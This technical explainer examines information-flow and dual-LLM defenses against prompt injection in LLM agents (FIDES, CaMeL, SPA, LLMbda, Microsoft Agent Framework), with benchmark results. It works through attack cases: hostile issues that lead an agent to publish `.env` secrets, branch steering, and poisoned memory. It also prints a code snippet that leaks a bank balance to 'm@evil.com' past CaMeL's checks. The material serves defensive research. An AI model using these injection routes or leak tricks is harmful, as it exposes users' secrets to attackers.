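    label(result) = label(call) ⊔ label(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(aₙ)
                    ⊔ labels of all stored data that f may read

if the planner wants to finish:
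    return the reply with its label
```

A tool's result inherits the label of the call because an attacker who influenced the choice of file has also influenced what the tool returns. In the triage example, FIDES would therefore label the contents of `.env` untrusted as well as private. Any stored data that the tool may have changed gets the same label as the result.

The policy engine is a function that accepts or rejects a labeled call. The two rules become:

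```
Trusted action:  label(call) ⊔ label(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(aₙ) is trusted
Permitted flow:  recipients ⊆ readers(a), for each argument a that the call sends
```

The permitted-flow rule alone doesn't prevent injection. An attacker could still choose what the agent writes to an authorized reader, but could not make it send private data to anyone else. If a tool call has to satisfy only one of the two rules, it can release private data to unauthorized readers only in a trusted context, where the framework assumes that the user intended the release. Security researchers call this robust declassification. Requiring both rules gives the strongest protection but blocks the most work.

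Microsoft's prototype for the chat service Teams applies the "either" version. If the context is trusted, the message goes out. If not, the policy engine looks up the channel's current members to find any who aren't allowed to read the content. If it finds any, it lists them and asks the user for approval.

### What Costa and colleagues proved

The labeled loop can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. To define it, take any run and fix its sequence of tool calls. Let `g` be the function that describes what this sequence does to the stored data. Then compare two versions of the stored data that differ only in their private parts:

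```
if d₁ and d₂ have the same public data,
then g(d₁) and g(d₂) have the same public data
```

Suppose a tool could attach a stored file to a public comment, and the agent attached `.env`. Changing the password in the file would change the comment, so the run would violate explicit secrecy.

The argument assumes that the model is deterministic, meaning that it always gives the same output for the same input, and that there is a correct account of everything each tool may read or write. It also assumes that the attacker can see changes to public data but not the timing or size of network messages.

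The definition fixes the sequence of calls, so it doesn't cover what an attacker could infer from which tools the agent chose. *SPA* (2026) limits this leak by also labeling the condition behind each choice. A stronger property, non-interference, would cover these leaks, but Costa and colleagues reject it as too restrictive because it would in effect forbid any public write after a call to a tool that may read private data.

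The definition of explicit secrecy also treats the conversation as part of the program, not as stored data, so it doesn't cover a password that the model reads and then types into a comment. The labels still cover that password, because the loop gives the model's reply the label of the whole conversation. For the triage agent, this labeling step matters more than the formal property.

### Security and task completion in AgentDojo

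Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, which has 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attacks in simulated workspace, travel, banking and Slack environments. They paired each task with every attack in the same environment. The attacker knew which tools the agent had and planted instructions for using them.

AgentDojo has no labels, so the researchers added their own. They marked a field untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. If any attack arrived in the body of an email, for example, they marked all email bodies untrusted. This tests enforcement clearly, but it guarantees that no attack can enter through a mislabeled field, so the results can't show how often developers would label real data correctly.

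Without policy checks, a basic agent running on GPT-4o carried out 152 injected tasks. FIDES without checks carried out 21, mainly because it keeps untrusted text in hidden variables that normally stay out of its main model's context. With checks, neither agent carried out any.

The researchers got the zeros by reading the logs themselves. AgentDojo's automatic scoring still counted three successful attacks against FIDES with checks, and more against the basic agent. Some of these were calls that the policy engine had blocked but AgentDojo counted anyway. Others were actions that the rules allowed, such as creating a calendar event with no other participants. A third group changed only the agent's answer, such as by making it recommend a particular hotel. The researchers reasonably exclude this group because no tool call broke a rule, but a user who booked the hotel would still have been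 misled.

The checks cost a lot of completed tasks. These are the percentages without any attack, using OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model than GPT-4o:

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| Basic, with checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| FIDES, with checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

On average across the four environments, the unprotected agent completed 84% of tasks, FIDES 61%, and the basic agent with checks 44%. With GPT-4o, FIDES outperformed the basic agent with checks by only 8 percentage points, because this weaker model often confused variable names or made unnecessary calls.

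Many tasks failed because the rules required a refusal. For example, several banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, but the file is untrusted, so the framework blocks the resulting payment. In about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks, the agent needs information from a tool result to choose its next step, compared with 5% in workspace and 10% in travel. Travel was the only environment where the basic agent with checks outperformed FIDES, because the rules allow many travel tools in an untrusted context as long as nothing private leaks.

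Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also worked on FIDES, argue that such comparisons make IFC look worse than it is, because the protected agent has to finish without any help while the unprotected one acts as if a person had approved every risky step. They counted how many tasks each agent could finish with and without human approvals. Using GPT-5, FIDES completed 57% of tasks with no approvals and 79% with as many as it needed. An agent without IFC that had to ask before every consequential action completed 35% without approvals and 72% with them. Telling the planning model about the labels and rules raised completion without approvals to 73%. GPT-5 is no longer a leading model, and the gains from o1 and GPT-5 suggest that newer models would do better still, although even a stronger model can't complete a task that the rules forbid.

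### Why the model call is the hard step

In ordinary code, a programmer can often see which inputs affect a result. If a program computes `z = x + y`, then `z` depends on `x` and `y` but not on another variable `w`. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) explains that in a language model, by contrast, any text in the conversation could in theory influence the next tool call, and the connections inside the model are complex and hard to observe.

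Removing one input and checking whether the output changes can miss hostile inputs. If two hostile issues contain the same instruction, removing either one leaves the other in place, so the output stays the same and both look harmless. Testing every combination would avoid this mistake, but ten inputs already have 1,024 combinations, and a model's output can vary between runs with identical inputs.

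Nobody has a reliable general method for calculating which inputs shaped an output. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this an open problem. The safe rule for now is to give the output the labels of everything the model read:

```
label(output) = ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ
```

This rule never misses an influence, but it also flags many that didn't occur. If the triage agent reads a stranger's issue and then copies a sentence from the project's license, the rule labels that sentence untrusted even though the issue didn't affect it. Over a long run, most outputs end up with the most restrictive label, a problem known as label creep.

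Zhong and colleagues found a way to use a narrower label without trusting a guess about what influenced the model's output. Before each model call, a screening program picks out the parts of the conversation that seem relevant. The framework joins their labels and blanks out every part whose label doesn't fit within that join. Suppose the triage agent has read a hostile issue, and the maintainer now asks it to correct the README file. If the screener selects only the request and the README, the framework removes the issue before the model writes the correction, so the correction is trusted.

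One of the screeners was a small neural network that identified relevant text with 81% accuracy on test data. Its mistakes mainly make the agent less useful, because they either hide text the model needed or add an unnecessary restriction, but that accuracy would be poor for a security check used on its own. An attacker might still influence which trusted text the screener keeps, but the attacker's words don't reach the model under a trusted label. In AgentDojo, the system stopped every targeted attack that broke its rules and completed about 2% fewer tasks under attack.

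Other researchers try to detect influence directly. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) describes methods that track variables, run the model several times or ask another model to inspect the record of a run. The first two can slow an agent considerably, and the third again relies on a model's judgment. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tested a tracker called NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios, where it missed 13 real cases of influence and raised 16 false alarms. Most of the misses involved text whose meaning had changed gradually over several steps. This accuracy is good for investigating past incidents, but it would be risky to allow tool calls based on the tracker alone, because an attacker can deliberately look for rewording that it misses.

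### Labeling contexts, messages and fields

Framework designers also have to decide how much text shares one label. The simplest choice is one label for the whole context, as in the triage example. A framework can also label each message separately, or each field within a message.

When a stranger opens a GitHub issue, GitHub assigns the number and creation date, and the stranger writes the title and body. If an agent reads the issue as a message with a single label, all four fields are untrusted, but if each field has its own label, the number and date can remain trusted. FIDES supports labels at any level of a structured tool result, and a label applies to everything below it unless a lower part has its own.

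Labeling each field separately helps only if the framework also keeps the untrusted fields away from the model. If it puts the whole record into the prompt, the context label combines the labels of all the fields, so one untrusted field makes the whole context untrusted. In one banking task, FIDES had to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. It showed the model the trusted amounts and dates but hid the untrusted descriptions. The model judged one transaction suspicious by its size alone, and since the context was still trusted, the framework allowed the password change.

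Flowsh has to use coarser units because a shell command can read many files and contact several servers. It gives each file one label and each server one label, then computes:

```
label(command) = label(context) ⊔ label(arguments)
                 ⊔ labels of all files opened
                 ⊔ labels of all servers contacted
```

Kim and colleagues count a file as read once a command opens it for reading, even if the command never reads the contents. Everything from GitHub's server gets the same label, whether it comes from the project's maintainers or a stranger. Flowsh also ignores the order of events within a command, so an untrusted file opened at the end affects the label of a file written at the start. These simplifications cause unnecessary restrictions, but they don't leave any influence unlabeled.

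Errors in finer labels can be more dangerous. A developer who labels a field trusted is claiming that no outsider can control it, and that claim is easy to get wrong for fields such as branch names and account names. A developer who isn't sure about a field can label the whole message untrusted and lose only some convenience.

### Inputs that need correct labels

The guarantee in FIDES starts from labels that someone else has supplied. For the triage agent, the main assumptions are:

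| Input | What FIDES assumes | How the assumption could fail |
|---|---|---|
| System and user messages | They are trusted, and public by default | A template inserts text from an issue |
| Tool descriptions | They are trusted | An outside server supplies them |
| Tool results | Their labels match where the data came from | `read_file` marks a stranger's proposed change as trusted |
| Reader lists | They include only people with permission | A former team member is still on the list |
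| Tools | The framework knows all the data they read and change | `write_file` starts a build that publishes a private file |

Costa and colleagues inferred some labels from the data itself, for instance by treating an email's sender and recipients as its readers. They suggest that a system could also relabel a document from untrusted to trusted after a classifier finds no injection in it. They warn that this weakens the guarantee, and adaptive attackers have beaten such classifiers most of the time.

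Zhong and colleagues likewise assume that developers supply the labels, and they treat unlabeled text as public and trusted, which makes this part of their design opt-in. They also describe how a tool can lose a label. If an agent sends itself a private message and another tool returns sent messages as public, the secret comes back labeled public. Attackers must also be unable to edit labels, so Flowsh discards any label that a shell command tries to write to a file and stores its own.

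One wrong label can reverse the outcome of the triage example. If a template pastes a hostile issue title into the opening prompt, as Cline's did, FIDES labels the title trusted and public by default. After the model reads `.env`, the context is trusted and private, so the trusted-action rule lets `post_comment` publish the secrets. Requiring both rules for `post_comment` would stop this leak, because the public may not read private data. But the attacker could still use `write_file`, which only requires a trusted context.

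## How do dual-LLM designs keep untrusted text away from the planning model?

A dual-LLM design divides an agent's work between two language models. The planning model decides which tools to call and never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. Malicious instructions in a bug report therefore don't reach the planning model, even if nobody labeled the report. An attacker can still feed false values into the planning model's steps, so later designs combine the split with labels and checks.

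### Willison's two models

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed the split, with a third component that he called the controller. The controller is ordinary software that runs the tools and keeps their results in variables. If a user asks for a summary of the latest email, the planning model requests steps like these:

```
$VAR1 = fetch_latest_emails(1)
$VAR2 = quarantined_llm("Summarize this: $VAR1")
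display("Your latest email, summarized: $VAR2")
```

The controller replaces `$VAR1` with the email just before it calls the quarantined model, and `$VAR2` with the summary just before it shows the user the answer. The planning model receives only the variable names and a notice that each step has finished. If the email contains an instruction to delete the whole mailbox, the quarantined model may try to follow it, but it can only write text.

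Willison allowed the planning model to see the quarantined model's output only when the quarantined model sorts text into a fixed set of categories and the controller has checked that its answer is one of them. All other output has to stay hidden, because a summary, for example, can contain the attacker's instructions.

He called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that passes raw text to the planning model would undo the protection. A hostile email could also still trick the user by making the summary ask them to copy encoded text into a website, and that text might contain their private data.

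Two years later, Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues found a flaw that Willison had missed, as he acknowledges in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025). Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's email address is in meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract the address, so an attacker who can edit the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. The assistant then follows the steps the user wanted but sends the document to the attacker.

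### How CaMeL runs a request

Debenedetti and colleagues designed CaMeL ("capabilities for machine learning"), in which a planning model turns the user's request into a complete program before any tool runs. A custom interpreter then executes the program, which is written in a restricted form of Python. The planning model also reads the tool descriptions, but not the tools' results.

The interpreter attaches metadata called capabilities to every value. Capabilities record where a value came from (its sources) and who may see it (its readers), as *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) explains. The interpreter also tracks which values the program used to compute others. Before each tool call, it runs a policy, a Python function that examines the arguments and their capabilities and returns either "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

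Suppose a maintainer asks the triage agent to answer issue 57 using whichever file the reporter mentions. The planning model might write this:

```python
issue = read_issue(57)
path = ask_quarantined("Which file does this report mention?", issue)
page = read_file(path)
answer = ask_quarantined("Answer the report from this file.", issue, page)
post_comment(57, answer)
```

An honest reporter mentions `docs/install.md`, and the program posts an answer based on the installation guide. An attacker instead plants an instruction to name `.env`. If the quarantined model obeys, the program still has the same five lines, but the third now reads the project's secrets and the fourth may copy them into the answer. The capabilities show the difference:

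| Value | Sources | Readers if the report is honest | Readers if the report is hostile |
|---|---|---|---|
| `issue` | The reporter | Anyone | Anyone |
| `path` | The reporter | Anyone | Anyone |
| `page` | The repository, at a path the reporter chose | Anyone | Maintainers |
| `answer` | The reporter and the repository | Anyone | Maintainers |

If `post_comment` has the permitted-flow rule from the previous section, the interpreter allows the call with the honest answer. With the hostile answer, it blocks the call or asks the maintainer to approve it, whereas a plain dual-LLM design would have posted the secrets.

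CaMeL's labels are also more precise than a single context label, which would block every file change after the agent read the issue. In CaMeL, a sixth line could still add the fixed sentence "Answered issue 57" to a log, because neither the sentence nor the decision to write it depends on the issue.

The interpreter checks each call against policy only when it reaches that call, so a long program may fail on its last line after the earlier steps have run. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check before execution. They convert the program into a model of every path it could take and test that model against rules such as "never disconnect a computer without approval". If a path breaks a rule, the planning model gets a description of that path and tries to repair the program.

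### CaMeL's results and token cost

In the revised version of their paper, Debenedetti and colleagues reported that CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. Other published results are lower:

| Test of CaMeL | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Published GPT-4o results, all four environments | 53.6% | 0% |
| Adapted run of the released code, all four environments | 29 of 97 | 0 of 629 |
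| GPT-5.2, banking only, policies off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2, banking only, policies on | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |

Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) quoted the GPT-4o results in *Indirect Prompt Injections* because they could not fully reproduce them. Without a defense, GPT-4o completed 83% of tasks in their tests, and 58% of attacks succeeded. The adapted run comes from *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defense. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran the banking tests for *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, with three attempts at each of 16 tasks.

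Security was strong in all four tests, but task completion varied widely. The tests used different models, policies and software adapters, so their results can't be combined into a single score for CaMeL. The two banking rows are the most directly comparable because only the policies changed. Turning the policies on cut completion from 67% to 37.5%, although both figures are uncertain because there were so few tasks.

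According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's developers recorded two successful attacks in their own evaluation. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a document, and the attacker changed the document. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and AgentDojo's scoring wrongly counted this as obeying the attacker.

CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as an ordinary agent on the median AgentDojo task. A cheaper model can process some of those tokens, because extracting an address from an email is easier than writing a program. Willison notes that the quarantined model could run on the user's own computer, so the company hosting the planning model would never receive the user's emails.

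### When FIDES shows the planning model an answer

The planning model in FIDES, the information-flow agent from the previous section, chooses one tool call at a time instead of following a complete program, and it receives some of the results. Costa and colleagues designed FIDES to hide a result only if it would make the context label more restrictive. When the agent reads an email, for example, the planning model might receive the trusted date but a placeholder such as `#read_emails_0.subject` instead of the subject. It can pass that placeholder to another tool, and FIDES inserts the real text when it makes the call.

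The decision to make a call can therefore have a different label from the text it sends. A policy might require the planning model to choose a message's recipient in a trusted context but allow the message itself to contain untrusted text.

Some tasks require the planning model to learn something about the hidden text. Suppose a user asks the agent to look through three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. FIDES can do this in five steps:

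1. It reads the emails into a variable.
2. The quarantined model answers whether they contain a meeting request, and FIDES stores the answer in a new variable.
3. The planning model opens that variable and sees "true" or "false".
4. If the answer is "true", the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
5. The planning model creates the event with those hidden details.

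The answer in step 3 comes from untrusted text, but constrained decoding limits what it can contain. This technique stops a model from generating any token that doesn't fit a specified format. FIDES adds the format to the label and ranks formats by how much information they can carry:

```
yes/no  ⊑  choice from a fixed list  ⊑  free text
```

A policy can let the planning model act on an untrusted yes-or-no answer but not on untrusted free text. An attacker can make the answer wrong, but a single bit can't carry a new instruction. A choice from a list of `n` options carries at most `log₂ n` bits, so a choice among eight categories carries at most three.

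The harm from a wrong answer depends on what the planning model does with it. If an attacker causes a false "yes", an unwanted calendar event would be a nuisance, but a deleted repository would be serious. Repeated queries also let an attacker pass more bits of information to the planning model. Costa and colleagues left constrained answers out of their AgentDojo tests because few tasks needed them, so the published results don't show how well this exception works in practice.

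### Keeping labels from one request to the next

An agent with memory can expose its planning model to text it retrieved earlier. In an example from *SPA*, published in August 2026, a user asks an agent on Monday to retrieve an invoice and remember its details, then tells it on Tuesday to pay the invoice. If the agent loads the whole invoice into the planning model's context on Tuesday, any instructions hidden in the invoice enter the context too. Even if the planning model ignores them, the agent may still pay the attacker's account.

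SPA, like CaMeL, plans before it runs any tools. Its plans use a much smaller language than CaMeL's, with steps for loading a stored result, calling a tool, asking the quarantined model, displaying something, branching and looping. The language has no arithmetic or text templates, so a checker can determine from the plan alone which values each step depends on. The checker computes all the labels in advance and rejects the entire plan if a tool call would break a rule. A step inside a branch inherits the label of the branch's condition, because the condition determines whether the step runs.

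SPA stores each result as content, a label and a description. The planning model writes most of the description when it plans the step, before the content is fetched. Suppose a request on Monday produces the details of an invoice. On Tuesday, the planning model sees only that the request produced those details, and it can plan a step that loads them. The account number comes back with its original untrusted label, so a payment tool that requires trusted input will reject it.

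The researchers tested SPA with the small model GPT-5.4-nano. They also split AgentDojo's 97 tasks into sequences of two to five requests to test the memory.

| Test | Label checks | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single requests | Off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Single requests | On | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Sequences of requests | Off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Sequences of requests | On | 35.3% | 0.2% |

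The 0.2% includes two runs that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plan. With label checks on, the agent loaded an available earlier result in about 90% of the cases where a task needed one, so it could usually find what it had stored even though the content was hidden. The checks disrupted tasks much more than hiding the content did. They rejected about 53% of the single-request plans, usually because a plan passed outside data to a tool that required trusted input.

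These tests provide little evidence about attacks stored in memory for later. When the researchers turned off label checks and let the planning model read stored content directly, only 0.6% of attacks succeeded, because AgentDojo's attacks mostly target the request in progress. An attacker who wrote text to target the planning model during a later request might succeed more often.

### Protection without a label

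With a single context label, mislabeling a hostile issue can let it trigger a dangerous tool call. A dual-LLM design keeps the issue from choosing the agent's steps without relying on labels. CaMeL's planning model finishes writing the program before the agent fetches issue 57, so the issue's text can't add a sixth line, even if its label is wrong or missing.

Garby and colleagues estimated how much protection comes from planning before the agent reads untrusted text. AgentDojo's banking tests pair 16 tasks with nine attacks, giving 144 combinations. In 97 of them, the attack needs a tool call or file that the plan for the user's task would never include, such as a money transfer during a request to summarize spending. Planning first should defeat those attacks without any label checks. The other 47 are harder to defend against because the plan already contains the call the attacker wants,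 and the attacker only has to change a value such as the account number.

Costa and colleagues similarly found that a version of their agent that never opened its variables allowed no real attacks, even without policy checks. FIDES itself allowed some real attacks without those checks because its planning model could open variables and read the hostile text.

The dual-LLM structure protects the choice of steps, but CaMeL still needs correct labels to protect the values that pass through them. If someone wrongly marked `.env` as readable by anyone, CaMeL would post the secrets from the worked example, even though the planning model had never read the issue.

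Even the choice of steps is safe only if untrusted text cannot reach the planning model by another route. Cline's template, which pasted an issue's title into the prompt, would also defeat CaMeL, because CaMeL treats the request as trusted. Messages between agents create the same problem. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents that each ran CaMeL, and an attack succeeded when one agent included a poisoned summary in its request to another.

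Untrusted text can also reach the planning model through tool descriptions. SPA has an optional mode in which the planning model never sees the descriptions of installed tools. Instead, a model invents tools for the task based only on the user's request, and a later step matches them to real ones. About three quarters of the runs failed at the matching step, so this mode isn't yet practical.

A planning model can also write a program that lets untrusted text decide which tools to call. One banking task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. In two of Garby and colleagues' runs without policies, CaMeL's planning model wrote a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. Whoever controlled the file could then choose the agent's actions, as in an ordinary agent, so the split between the models no longer helped. Policies can catch the resulting calls.

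### False values can steer a fixed plan

Many useful plans contain a branch. For example, the triage agent might close an issue if the quarantined model judges it to be a duplicate and otherwise notify a maintainer. An attacker who wants to suppress a report of a serious flaw could add a comment falsely claiming that the team has already fixed the flaw. The agent would then close the report while following only steps that the planning model wrote.

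In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) studied agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. Their planning model writes a program without seeing the screen, and a quarantined model answers questions such as where to click to dismiss a cookie notice. In an attack they call branch steering, the researchers disguised an advertisement as a cookie notice. The program contained a step for closing such notices, so the agent clicked the advertisement and went to the attacker's website.

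They tried to catch these false answers by checking them against the page's code or asking a second model to look at the screenshot. The page check caught the fake notice in some advertisements but missed it in others. The second model could not reliably catch fake notices without also rejecting many legitimate clicks. Another attack, which slightly altered the pixels of an advertisement, got past both checks.

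Policies like CaMeL's are of little use for a tool like `click(x, y)`, which could do anything from closing a notice to making a purchase. Tools such as `post_comment` have a clearer purpose, so a developer can specify who may receive which data. But no policy about sources and readers can establish whether a permitted statement is true. If the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file, and an attacker replaces the bill, no label distinguishes the fake bill from a real one by the same author.

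### Plans that depend on what the agent reads

A request such as "do the tasks on my to-do list that are due today" is hard to plan in advance, because the planning model doesn't know what the tasks are. It can write a branch for every kind of task it expects, but any unexpected task will fail. An ordinary agent would read the list and then decide. Many of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks have this problem. In tests with GPT-4o, Costa and colleagues found that policy checks lowered FIDES's task completion more in those two environments than in workspace or travel.

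Computer use is an extreme case, since almost every click depends on what is on the screen. Foerster and colleagues instructed the planning model to check the state of the screen before each action and prepare for several possibilities. The programs became much longer:

| Average per program | AgentDojo | Computer use |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 5 | 41 |
| Branches | 4 | 40 |

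About half of the steps in the computer-use programs were fallbacks that did not run. Of 109 tasks that an unprotected agent using Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed, the protected version completed 31 on the first attempt and 62 within five attempts. Success depended mainly on the planning model rather than the model that processed the screen, so stronger models will probably narrow the gap between the two versions.

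The researchers also adapted FIDES, which can adjust its plan after a constrained answer. On 60 tasks, it performed about as well as CaMeL. CaMeL's version added 1.88 times the unprotected agent's total token use, while FIDES's added 29.6 times that total because it sent the whole history to the planning model again at every step.

### Leaks in CaMeL's label tracking

A program can reveal a secret without ever copying it. Suppose a bank's agent runs this line:

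```python
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The message is a fixed word, but its arrival tells the recipient that the balance is high. CaMeL handles this case correctly. The interpreter knows that the call depends on a secret condition, so it blocks the email. Garby and colleagues showed that a slightly longer program gets around the check, using a trick that computer scientists have known since the 1970s:

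```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when an assignment to it runs under a secret condition. It does nothing for an assignment that it skips, and here the skipped assignment gives the secret away:

| | High balance | Low balance |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp` after line 3 | False, secret | True, public |
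| Does line 4 change `rich`? | No | Yes |
| `rich` after line 4 | True, public | False, public |
| Is the email sent? | Yes | No |

In both cases `rich` ends up with a public label, although its value reveals the balance. An interpreter that labels only what it executes can't track the information revealed by skipping line 4. SPA's language prevents this particular pattern, because a value created inside a branch can't be used after the branch ends, and its checker examines both branches before the plan runs.

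Another leak comes from the code around CaMeL's interpreter. If a program fails, an ordinary Python loop prompts the planning model to try again, and CaMeL doesn't track labels through that loop. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit of it. One bit may not matter, but repeated retries can reveal the whole secret. The loop also returns error messages to the planning model. CaMeL censors them to keep out untrusted text, but there is no formal guarantee that the censoring works.

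Garby and colleagues found a simpler mistake in the handling of text templates. Inserting an untrusted value into a larger piece of text made the resulting text trusted. Python programs often use expressions like `f"Reported by {name}"`, so this could happen without anyone trying to leak anything.

An attacker who only controls an issue can't write the bank program above, because the planning model never reads the issue. The planning model would have to write such a program by accident, or someone would have to influence it through another route, such as a malicious tool description. The branch leak is therefore less urgent than an ordinary injection, but it still matters for a system that is supposed to enforce its policies on any program the planning model writes.

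### What the LLMbda calculus proves

Garby and colleagues responded with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. A program in LLMbda can query a model, start a separate conversation for untrusted text, run code that a model wrote, and check labels. Every value and every conversation has a label. If a program tries to add a message to a public conversation because of a secret condition, the interpreter stops it, because the message's presence or absence would reveal whether the condition was true.

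They proved a version of noninterference, the stronger property that Costa and colleagues considered too restrictive for FIDES. Take two starting points that differ only in things an observer may not see. For each outcome `q` that the observer can see, let `μ₁(q)` and `μ₂(q)` be its probability from each starting point. The theorem guarantees that some function `ω` satisfies:

```
μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q)  and  μ₂(q) ≤ ω(q)   for every q
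the sum of ω(q) over all q is at most 1
```

The probabilities in `μ₁` and in `μ₂` may each add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish. A run that stops at a failed label check also counts as unfinished. If every run finishes, the two sets of probabilities must be identical, so the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the distance between them is at most the average chance of not finishing. If 2% of runs are unfinished from one starting point and 4% from the other, the distance is at most 3 percentage points.

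The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that a model generates during a run. The researchers checked the proof with Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs, and also wrote the interpreter in Lean. The theorem therefore applies to the interpreter that runs the agent, not just to a simplified description of it.

LLMbda also has an explicit `endorse` command. For example, a program can ask a quarantined model to sort an email into one of a few categories, confirm that the answer is one of those categories, and endorse the answer for use as a subject line. A second theorem guarantees that endorsing data can't make secret data public. As with Django's `mark_safe`, a reviewer can search for every use of the command.

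To test the language, Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori and ran it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Its planning model first tries its programs on invented data, so error messages from failed trials contain nothing an attacker wrote. Only a program that works on the invented data is then run on the real accounts. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 attempts, twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded.

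Part of that advantage comes from a looser rule that lets Randori's planning model endorse untrusted data when it writes the program, whereas CaMeL's policies refused such data in these tests. When the planning model wasn't allowed to endorse data, Randori's score fell from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. Both successful attacks depended on an endorsement. The user had asked the agent to pay as a file instructed, the attacker had replaced the file's contents, and the program endorsed whatever the file contained. The theorems don't rule this out, because they protect secrets from leaking and don't cover whether the planning model was right to trust the file.

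## What do agent frameworks do with content that nobody labeled?

Agent frameworks differ in how they treat unlabeled content. Microsoft Agent Framework, a library for building agents, has no trust labels until a developer turns on its security module. The module's default for unlabeled tool output became stricter after launch. GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs agents on a project's issues and code, automatically assigns a trust level to each GitHub item. On public repositories, it hides most outsiders' text unless the maintainers lower the trust threshold.

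| Software | Content nobody labeled | Automatic propagation | Checks before an action | At installation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Agent Framework, May 2026 | Trusted and public | Yes | Where a tool declares a rule | Off |
| Microsoft Agent Framework, later documentation | Tool output is untrusted and public | Yes | Apparently only where a tool declares a rule | Off |
| GitHub Agentic Workflows, public repository | GitHub assigns a level | Low-level items never reach the model | Separate limits on outputs | On |
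| GitHub Agentic Workflows, private repository | Everything counts as approved | No filter | Separate limits on outputs | Filter off |
| GitHub's Model Context Protocol server with Copilot CLI | The server labels results by the repository's visibility | Yes, through a context label | For selected GitHub tools | Off |

### Message roles without the security module

In a Microsoft agent without the module, a message's role is the main sign of where its text came from. Under Microsoft's safety guidance, the system role is the most trusted and must never contain outside text, while user, assistant and tool messages are untrusted. If a developer's code adds text without a role, the framework assigns the user role, so a bug report added this way doesn't become a developer's instruction.

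This ranking is advisory and doesn't control the tools. By default, the framework runs any tool the model requests without asking the user, whatever messages came before. A role records where text sits in the conversation, not who wrote it, so an issue title pasted into the system message gets the highest trust. Microsoft warns that components supplying memories or retrieved documents can add messages in any role, including system. It also warns that an attacker who tampers with a saved session could promote a message to a more trusted role.

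LangChain, another widely used framework, offers add-ons that screen content. Its documentation shows how to import a content filter from Microsoft's Azure service, one that looks for hate and violence, and pass it to the function that creates an agent. A polite request to post the contents of `.env` contains neither, so this kind of screen can't replace a trust label, even when a developer remembers to add it.

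### Turning on Microsoft's module

The security module is Microsoft's implementation of FIDES, the information-flow design by Costa and colleagues. It has shipped in the framework's core Python package since version 1.3.0, and Microsoft marks it as experimental. According to Microsoft's documentation, a .NET version is coming soon.

A developer turns the module on by attaching a `SecureAgentConfig` object to an agent. The object installs middleware, code that runs before and after each tool call to update the context label and enforce the tools' rules. Confidentiality has a third level above private, called `user_identity`, for credentials and personal data.

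In Microsoft's version of the triage agent, `read_file` labels everything it returns as private. Microsoft gives the agent this tool so that it can quote relevant source code in its replies, but after reading any file, even a published one, the agent can't post a public comment without approval.

Microsoft suggests leaving the module off for prototypes and for agents with no dangerous tools, and says developers can add it later without rewriting their tools. The program will still run, but tools written without labels in mind have no labels on their output and no rules about when they may run, so the protection depends on the module's defaults for such tools.

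### A stricter default for integrity but not for secrets

In its launch post of May 20, 2026, Microsoft listed the module's permissive default as a limitation. A tool that a developer forgot to label counted as trusted and public. Microsoft asked developers whether treating such tools as untrusted would be worth the trouble.

The later documentation adopts the stricter answer. A setting called `default_integrity` now starts as untrusted, and Microsoft advises changing it to trusted only for a closed set of fully vetted tools. The matching setting for secrecy, `default_confidentiality`, still starts as public. Microsoft describes the combination as failing closed, but that is true of only half the label. Suppose a developer copies the example configuration and forgets one label:

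| Forgotten label | Launch default | Later default |
|---|---|---|
| Output of `read_issue` | The issue counts as trusted, so it can prompt a change through `write_file` | The issue counts as untrusted, so `write_file` refuses |
| Output of `read_file` | The `.env` file counts as public, so `post_comment` can publish it | The `.env` file still counts as public, so `post_comment` can publish it |

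The attack in the second row works because Microsoft's `post_comment` has a rule about secrecy but none about integrity. The module marks the context as untrusted, but no rule on that tool checks the mark.

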